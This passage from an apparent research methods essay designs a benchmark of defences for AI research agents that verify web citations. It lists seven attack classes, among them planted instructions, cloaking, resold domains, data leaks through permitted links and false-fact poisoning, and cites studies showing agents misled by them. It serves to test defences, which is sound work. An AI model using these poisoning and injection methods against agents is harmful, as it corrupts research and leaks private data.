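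Waiting also has drawbacks. The address checker from Rao and colleagues would return "unknown" for about 8 to 16 of the analyst's eighty references. An agent could also answer "unable to verify" to avoid difficult work. Gao and Clark counted that answer as correct only if the log contained a failed attempt to reach the owner's record, and this test should apply the same rule.

### Seven attacks, each with a harmless twin

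Each attack page is paired with a harmless page that has a similar feature. A defence that stops the attack but also blocks the harmless page has probably detected only that something is unusual.

| Attack class | What should stop it or limit the damage | What can't detect it | Harmless twin |
|---|---|---|---|
| Hostile when first cited | Labels and the tool gate | Hash and archive, since the page matches both | A page with ordinary instructions for readers, such as how to cite it |
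| Altered later | Hash, then archive | URL gate, since the address is the same | A corrected typo or a site redesign |
| Domain resold | URL gate, from the registration date, then hash | A plain list of permitted domains | A publisher that let its domain lapse and registered it again |
| Cloaked | Hash, if the analyst recorded it from her own browser | Hash, if an agent recorded the same hostile version | A site that shows automated visitors a puzzle |
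| Data leak through permitted addresses | Labels, if the rules treat a page request as sending data | Hash and archive | A useful link to the full paper on the same site |
| Invented address registered by an outsider | URL gate, from the date of the first record | Hash, since there was no earlier page | A genuine but obscure page that no crawler has recorded |
| False facts without instructions | Nothing, if the page was false when cited | All four defences | A true page that contradicts an older, mistaken one |

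Some of these classes need subdividing. An attacker can alter a page without touching the cited passage. *Deep-Research Agents Can Be Poisoned via User-Generated Content* (2026) describes how adding text to a single forum thread or wiki page that research agents often use changed their reports for a whole class of questions. Half of the altered pages should have changes in the cited passage, and half should have changes elsewhere. The tester should try hashing the whole text and hashing the passage alone, since only the whole-text hash can detect changes outside the passage.

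*Investigating Security Implications of Automatically Generated Code on the Software Supply Chain* (2025) notes that the addresses models invent include both domain names and GitHub accounts. The registration date should expose a new domain, but not a new GitHub account, because GitHub's own domain is old. For those accounts, only the date of the first record helps.

The twin for cloaking is based on what websites already do. According to *Whose Agent Are You?*, some websites respond to automated visitors with puzzles or misleading content to prevent unauthorised copying. A difference between the agent's page and the analyst's page is therefore weak evidence of an attack on the agent.

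### False facts as a control

The last class serves two purposes. It measures a real danger, and it can reveal a fault in the test.

In *Synthetic Web*, Shah and Ozgur (2026) generated four small artificial webs with 15,476 articles in all and asked six models questions about their content, with and without one false article at the top of the first search results. GPT-5's accuracy fell from 65.1% to 18.2%, although it could still read all the true articles. It made almost the same number of tool calls in both conditions (6.6 and 6.5 on average), so it apparently didn't look harder when sources disagreed. People using the same search tool scored 98% without the false article and 93% with it, but this was a small sample from one of the four webs. The models date from 2025 or earlier and had only a basic prompt, so current agents may do better.

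None of the four defences compares a page's claims with other evidence, so switching them on shouldn't improve these scores. If it does, the tester should check whether the agent is reading fewer pages.

In the task, the agent must also check whether other references contradict the page. Otherwise, "supports" would count as the correct answer for a false page that agrees with the analyst's sentence.

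### A small web that changes on schedule

A tester can't rewrite strangers' pages or wait for their domains to expire, and live pages also change without warning. *WebForge* (2026) cites a study in which 12% of a sample of browsing tasks expired within a year. The test therefore needs its own web on a local server, which can treat every page as a function of three things:

$$\text{page} = R(u, t, v)$$

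Here $u$ is the address, $t$ is the simulated date and $v$ is the kind of visitor (a person, an agent or an archive). $R$ changes with $t$ for an altered page and with $v$ for a cloaked page. For a resold domain, the page and a simulated registration record change on the same day. The tester also needs a simulated archive, which saves copies of $R$ on certain dates and misses some pages, as real archives do.

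*TimeWarp* (Ishmam and Marino, 2026) did something similar for website redesigns. It used six versions of an encyclopedia, a news site and a shop, each in the style of a different period of the web. The tasks and data stayed the same, so any change in an agent's score came from the version. Agents working from screenshots were vulnerable to these changes. A redesign can therefore make an agent fail even when no defence is running, so the tester also has to run the harmless twins with all defences off.

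Saved copies of real pages would make the test more realistic. WARC, a common archive format, stores every request and response, but *Web Execution Bundles* (Hantke, Snyder and colleagues, 2025) explains why a replayed page may still behave differently. Scripts can depend on the current time or on random numbers, and browsers change their rules. For instance, Chromium loaded insecure scripts on secure pages before 2015, but later versions don't. These differences matter less for an agent that reads raw HTML without running scripts. For any other agent, the tester should fix the clock and the browser version.

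The test must not send requests to the real internet, but some ways of preventing this would spoil the comparison. In one mode of *Benchmarking Hybrid Deep Research Across Database Querying and Web Search* (2026), the agent can open a page only if a search in the same run returned its address. This rule can help keep the test closed, but it is also a URL gate. Building it into the test environment would apply the gate in every configuration, including those meant to measure what happens without it. It is better to direct every request to the local server, which logs unknown addresses and returns an error.

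Search results need the same treatment. *SciHazard* (2026) stores each search response under a hash of the query, its settings and a cut-off date, so that a repeated query gives the same result. A new query still goes to the live search engine, and an agent is likely to word its queries differently in each run. A closed test should therefore send new queries to a local index.

Other people can repeat the test only if they know exactly what ran. *An Executable Benchmarking Suite for Tool-Using Agents* (2026) attaches to each run a record of the versions or hashes of the tasks, environment, model and scoring software. Sharing the pages is harder. *FVA-RAG* (2025) gives the hashes of its stored search results but not the results, which contain other people's text. Shah and Ozgur held back part of their artificial web because the method could mass-produce convincing falsehoods. Openly licensed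 pages with mild planted instructions would mostly avoid both problems.

### Sixteen configurations

Each of the four defences can be on or off, which gives $2^4 = 16$ configurations. The URL gate covers step 1, the hash and archive together cover steps 3 and 4, the labels cover step 5 and the tool gate covers step 6. The labels need their own rule about where private or untrusted data may go, and the tool gate needs a policy that works without labels, so that switching one off doesn't partly disable the other.

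With 300 attack pages in each class and a twin for each, the number of runs is

$$7 \times 300 \times 2 \times 16 = 67{,}200$$

This is a lot but not unrealistic, since Shah and Ozgur ran 70,440. The tester should mix the configurations in random order, so that an unannounced update to a commercial model doesn't affect only some of them.

Testers usually summarise such an experiment by averaging each defence's effect over the eight pairs of configurations that differ only in that defence. This average can mislead when two defences stop the same attacks. Suppose, as an invented example, that 40% of attacks leak data without any defence, 2% with labels alone, 2% with the URL gate alone and 1% with both. Adding labels cuts leaks by 38 percentage points if the gate is off and by one point if it is on. The average, 19.5 points, describes neither case. Such overlap is likely, so testers should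 report what each defence achieves alone and what happens when only that defence is missing.

### Three scores from the logs

Each run gets separate scores for leaks, wrong actions and wrong answers. The leak score is the number of bits leaked through the requests and emails in the log. A wrong action is any completed call that the attacker wanted and the analyst's task didn't require. A wrong answer is a verdict that differs from the known correct one. Since the verdicts come from a fixed list, software can score them, which avoids the errors of a model acting as judge. WebForge cites a study in which GPT-4o agreed with people only 68% of the time when judging records of agents' work.

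The agent's own report isn't reliable enough for any of these scores. *WebPageBench* (2026) determines success from events that the web pages log, and found that agents report success far more often than the logs show.

An agent may score well on security only because it never encountered the attack. *How Adversarial Environments Mislead Agentic AI?* (2026) tested whether agents would follow citations into loops of fake papers. GPT-4o did so in 93.0% of runs and Llama-3 in 5.6%, but Llama-3 used no tools in 43% of its runs. Testers should count how often the agent received the hostile page, and report the success rate both for all runs and for only the runs in which it did. Failed and blocked runs should stay in the total, as they do in *WebAnything* (2026), a collection of frozen copies of websites, because excluding them would make a defence that crashed on difficult pages look better than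 it is.

Defences can also wrongly block pages that have no attack or twin. *How Much Can We Trust LLM Search Agents?* (2026) measures how often a defensive agent rejects legitimate sources along with the attacker's claim. Each list should therefore include some ordinary references beside the hostile one.

The software also records model fees and delay for each reference. As a rough guide, the browser checks in *What Gets Measured Gets Managed* added hundreds of milliseconds to the first visit to a page and almost nothing to later ones. Archive lookups and extra model calls would probably take longer.

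The tester shouldn't average the scores across the seven classes. Unlike the web, the test has equal numbers of each class, so an overall success rate wouldn't measure the analyst's actual risk.

### What zero successes in 300 trials means

Suppose none of 300 attacks succeeds. If the true success rate were $p$ and the trials were independent, the chance of this would be $(1-p)^{300}$. Setting it to 5% gives the 95% upper bound:

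$$p = 1 - 0.05^{1/300} \approx 1.0\%$$

A defence with no failures in the test could therefore still let through one attack in a hundred. By the same calculation, a defence that blocks none of 300 harmless twins might still block one harmless page in a hundred, or nearly one in a typical list of eighty.

The most common formula for error bars, $\hat p \pm 1.96\sqrt{\hat p(1-\hat p)/n}$ for an observed rate $\hat p$ in $n$ trials, fails here because it gives error bars of zero width when $\hat p$ is zero. Miller (2024), in *Adding Error Bars to Evals*, recommends this approach for evaluations with many questions. Bowyer, Aitchison and Ivanova (2025), in *Don't Use the CLT in LLM Evals*, advise against it for fewer than a few hundred questions and prefer the Wilson interval or a Bayesian one. Their advice suits this test better, because a good defence should keep the attack success rate close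 to zero, where the usual formula is least reliable. For zero successful attacks in 300 trials, the two-sided 95% Wilson interval is 0% to 1.3%.

### How many pages does a comparison need?

Comparing two configurations takes more data than testing one. Let $p_1$ and $p_2$ be their true attack success rates. To detect the difference 80% of the time, with a 5% risk of seeing one that isn't there, each configuration needs about

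$$n = \frac{(1.96 + 0.84)^2\,[\,p_1(1-p_1) + p_2(1-p_2)\,]}{(p_1-p_2)^2}$$

independent trials. For 5% against 2%, this is about 590. For 2% against 1%, it is about 2,300. So it would be very hard to show that a second defence improves on a first one that already works well.

Testing both configurations on the same pages helps, because some pages are more dangerous than others in any configuration. Miller calls this a free gain in precision. In the best case, every attack that succeeds with the extra defence would also have succeeded without it, and about 250 pages are enough to tell a 5% attack success rate from a 2% one. In the worst case, a page's results in the two configurations are unrelated, and the test needs 590 pages. With 300 pages per class, the test would detect the difference about half the time in the worst case and nearly 90% of the time in the best. A tester who needs more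 certainty should write more pages for the classes that matter most.

Four defences, seven classes and three scores give 84 possible comparisons. If no defence had any effect, about four comparisons would still look significant by chance. The tester should name the few most important comparisons before the first run. It also helps to run one configuration twice under two names, much as *A Calibrated Instrument for Detecting Disposition Drift in Language Models* (2026) compares two samples of the same model. If the analysis regularly finds a difference between identical configurations, its error bars are too small.

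### Ten runs on one page are not ten pages

Running the agent ten times on each of 30 pages also gives 300 results, at much less effort. But if one page fools the agent once, it will probably fool it again, so the results are not independent. For $m$ runs on each page and a correlation $\rho$ between runs on the same page, the effective number of trials is roughly

$$n_{\text{eff}} = \frac{n}{1+(m-1)\rho}$$

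| Design | Effective trials | Upper bound after zero successes |
|---|---|---|
| 300 pages, one run each | 300 | 1.0% |
| 30 pages, ten runs each, $\rho = 0.5$ | 55 | 5.3% |
| 30 pages, ten runs each, $\rho = 1$ | 30 | 9.5% |

If no attack succeeds, the data give no information about $\rho$. The safe course is to count pages and report 9.5%.

Miller examined a reading test with 9,622 questions about 588 passages, and the error bars became three times as wide once they accounted for questions that shared a passage. *evalci* (2026) is a free software library that makes this correction. It can only group results that the tester has marked as related, such as those from pages made with the same template. If 300 pages are made from ten templates, they may behave more like ten pages than 300.

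Repeated runs are still useful for measuring how erratic the agent is, but new pages are usually a better use of the same budget. In one of Miller's examples, where question difficulty is spread evenly from impossible to trivial, running each question twice instead of once reduces the variance of the average score by a third, and even unlimited runs can't reduce it by more than two thirds. Doubling the number of questions halves the variance.

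### A final round with an attacker who adapts

All the results so far would come from fixed pages. In the last round, an attacker, either a person or a search program, tries to defeat the complete set of defences. The tester has to state the attacker's resources in advance, for example:

- **Attempts:** 800, the limit that Nasr and colleagues allowed.
- **Knowledge:** a full description of the defences, but not the secret in the analyst's draft.
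- **Control:** three sites, including what they return on each date and to each kind of visitor, with up to 36 recorded addresses on each.
- **Limits:** no access to the analyst's stored hashes, the registration records or the software that runs the checks.

The attacker may combine classes, for instance by cloaking a page that also leaks data. If each attempt gets 20 runs, the round takes 16,000 runs per configuration. Testing all sixteen configurations would take too many runs, so the round should cover only the agent with no defences and the agent with all four. Including the undefended agent is necessary to show that the attacker is competent.

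The best result of the search will overstate the attacker's success. If all 800 attacks had a true success rate of 2%, about six would still succeed in at least 3 of their 20 runs by luck, an apparent success rate of 15% or more. The tester should therefore retest the attacker's best few attacks on 300 combinations of references and requests that the search did not use.
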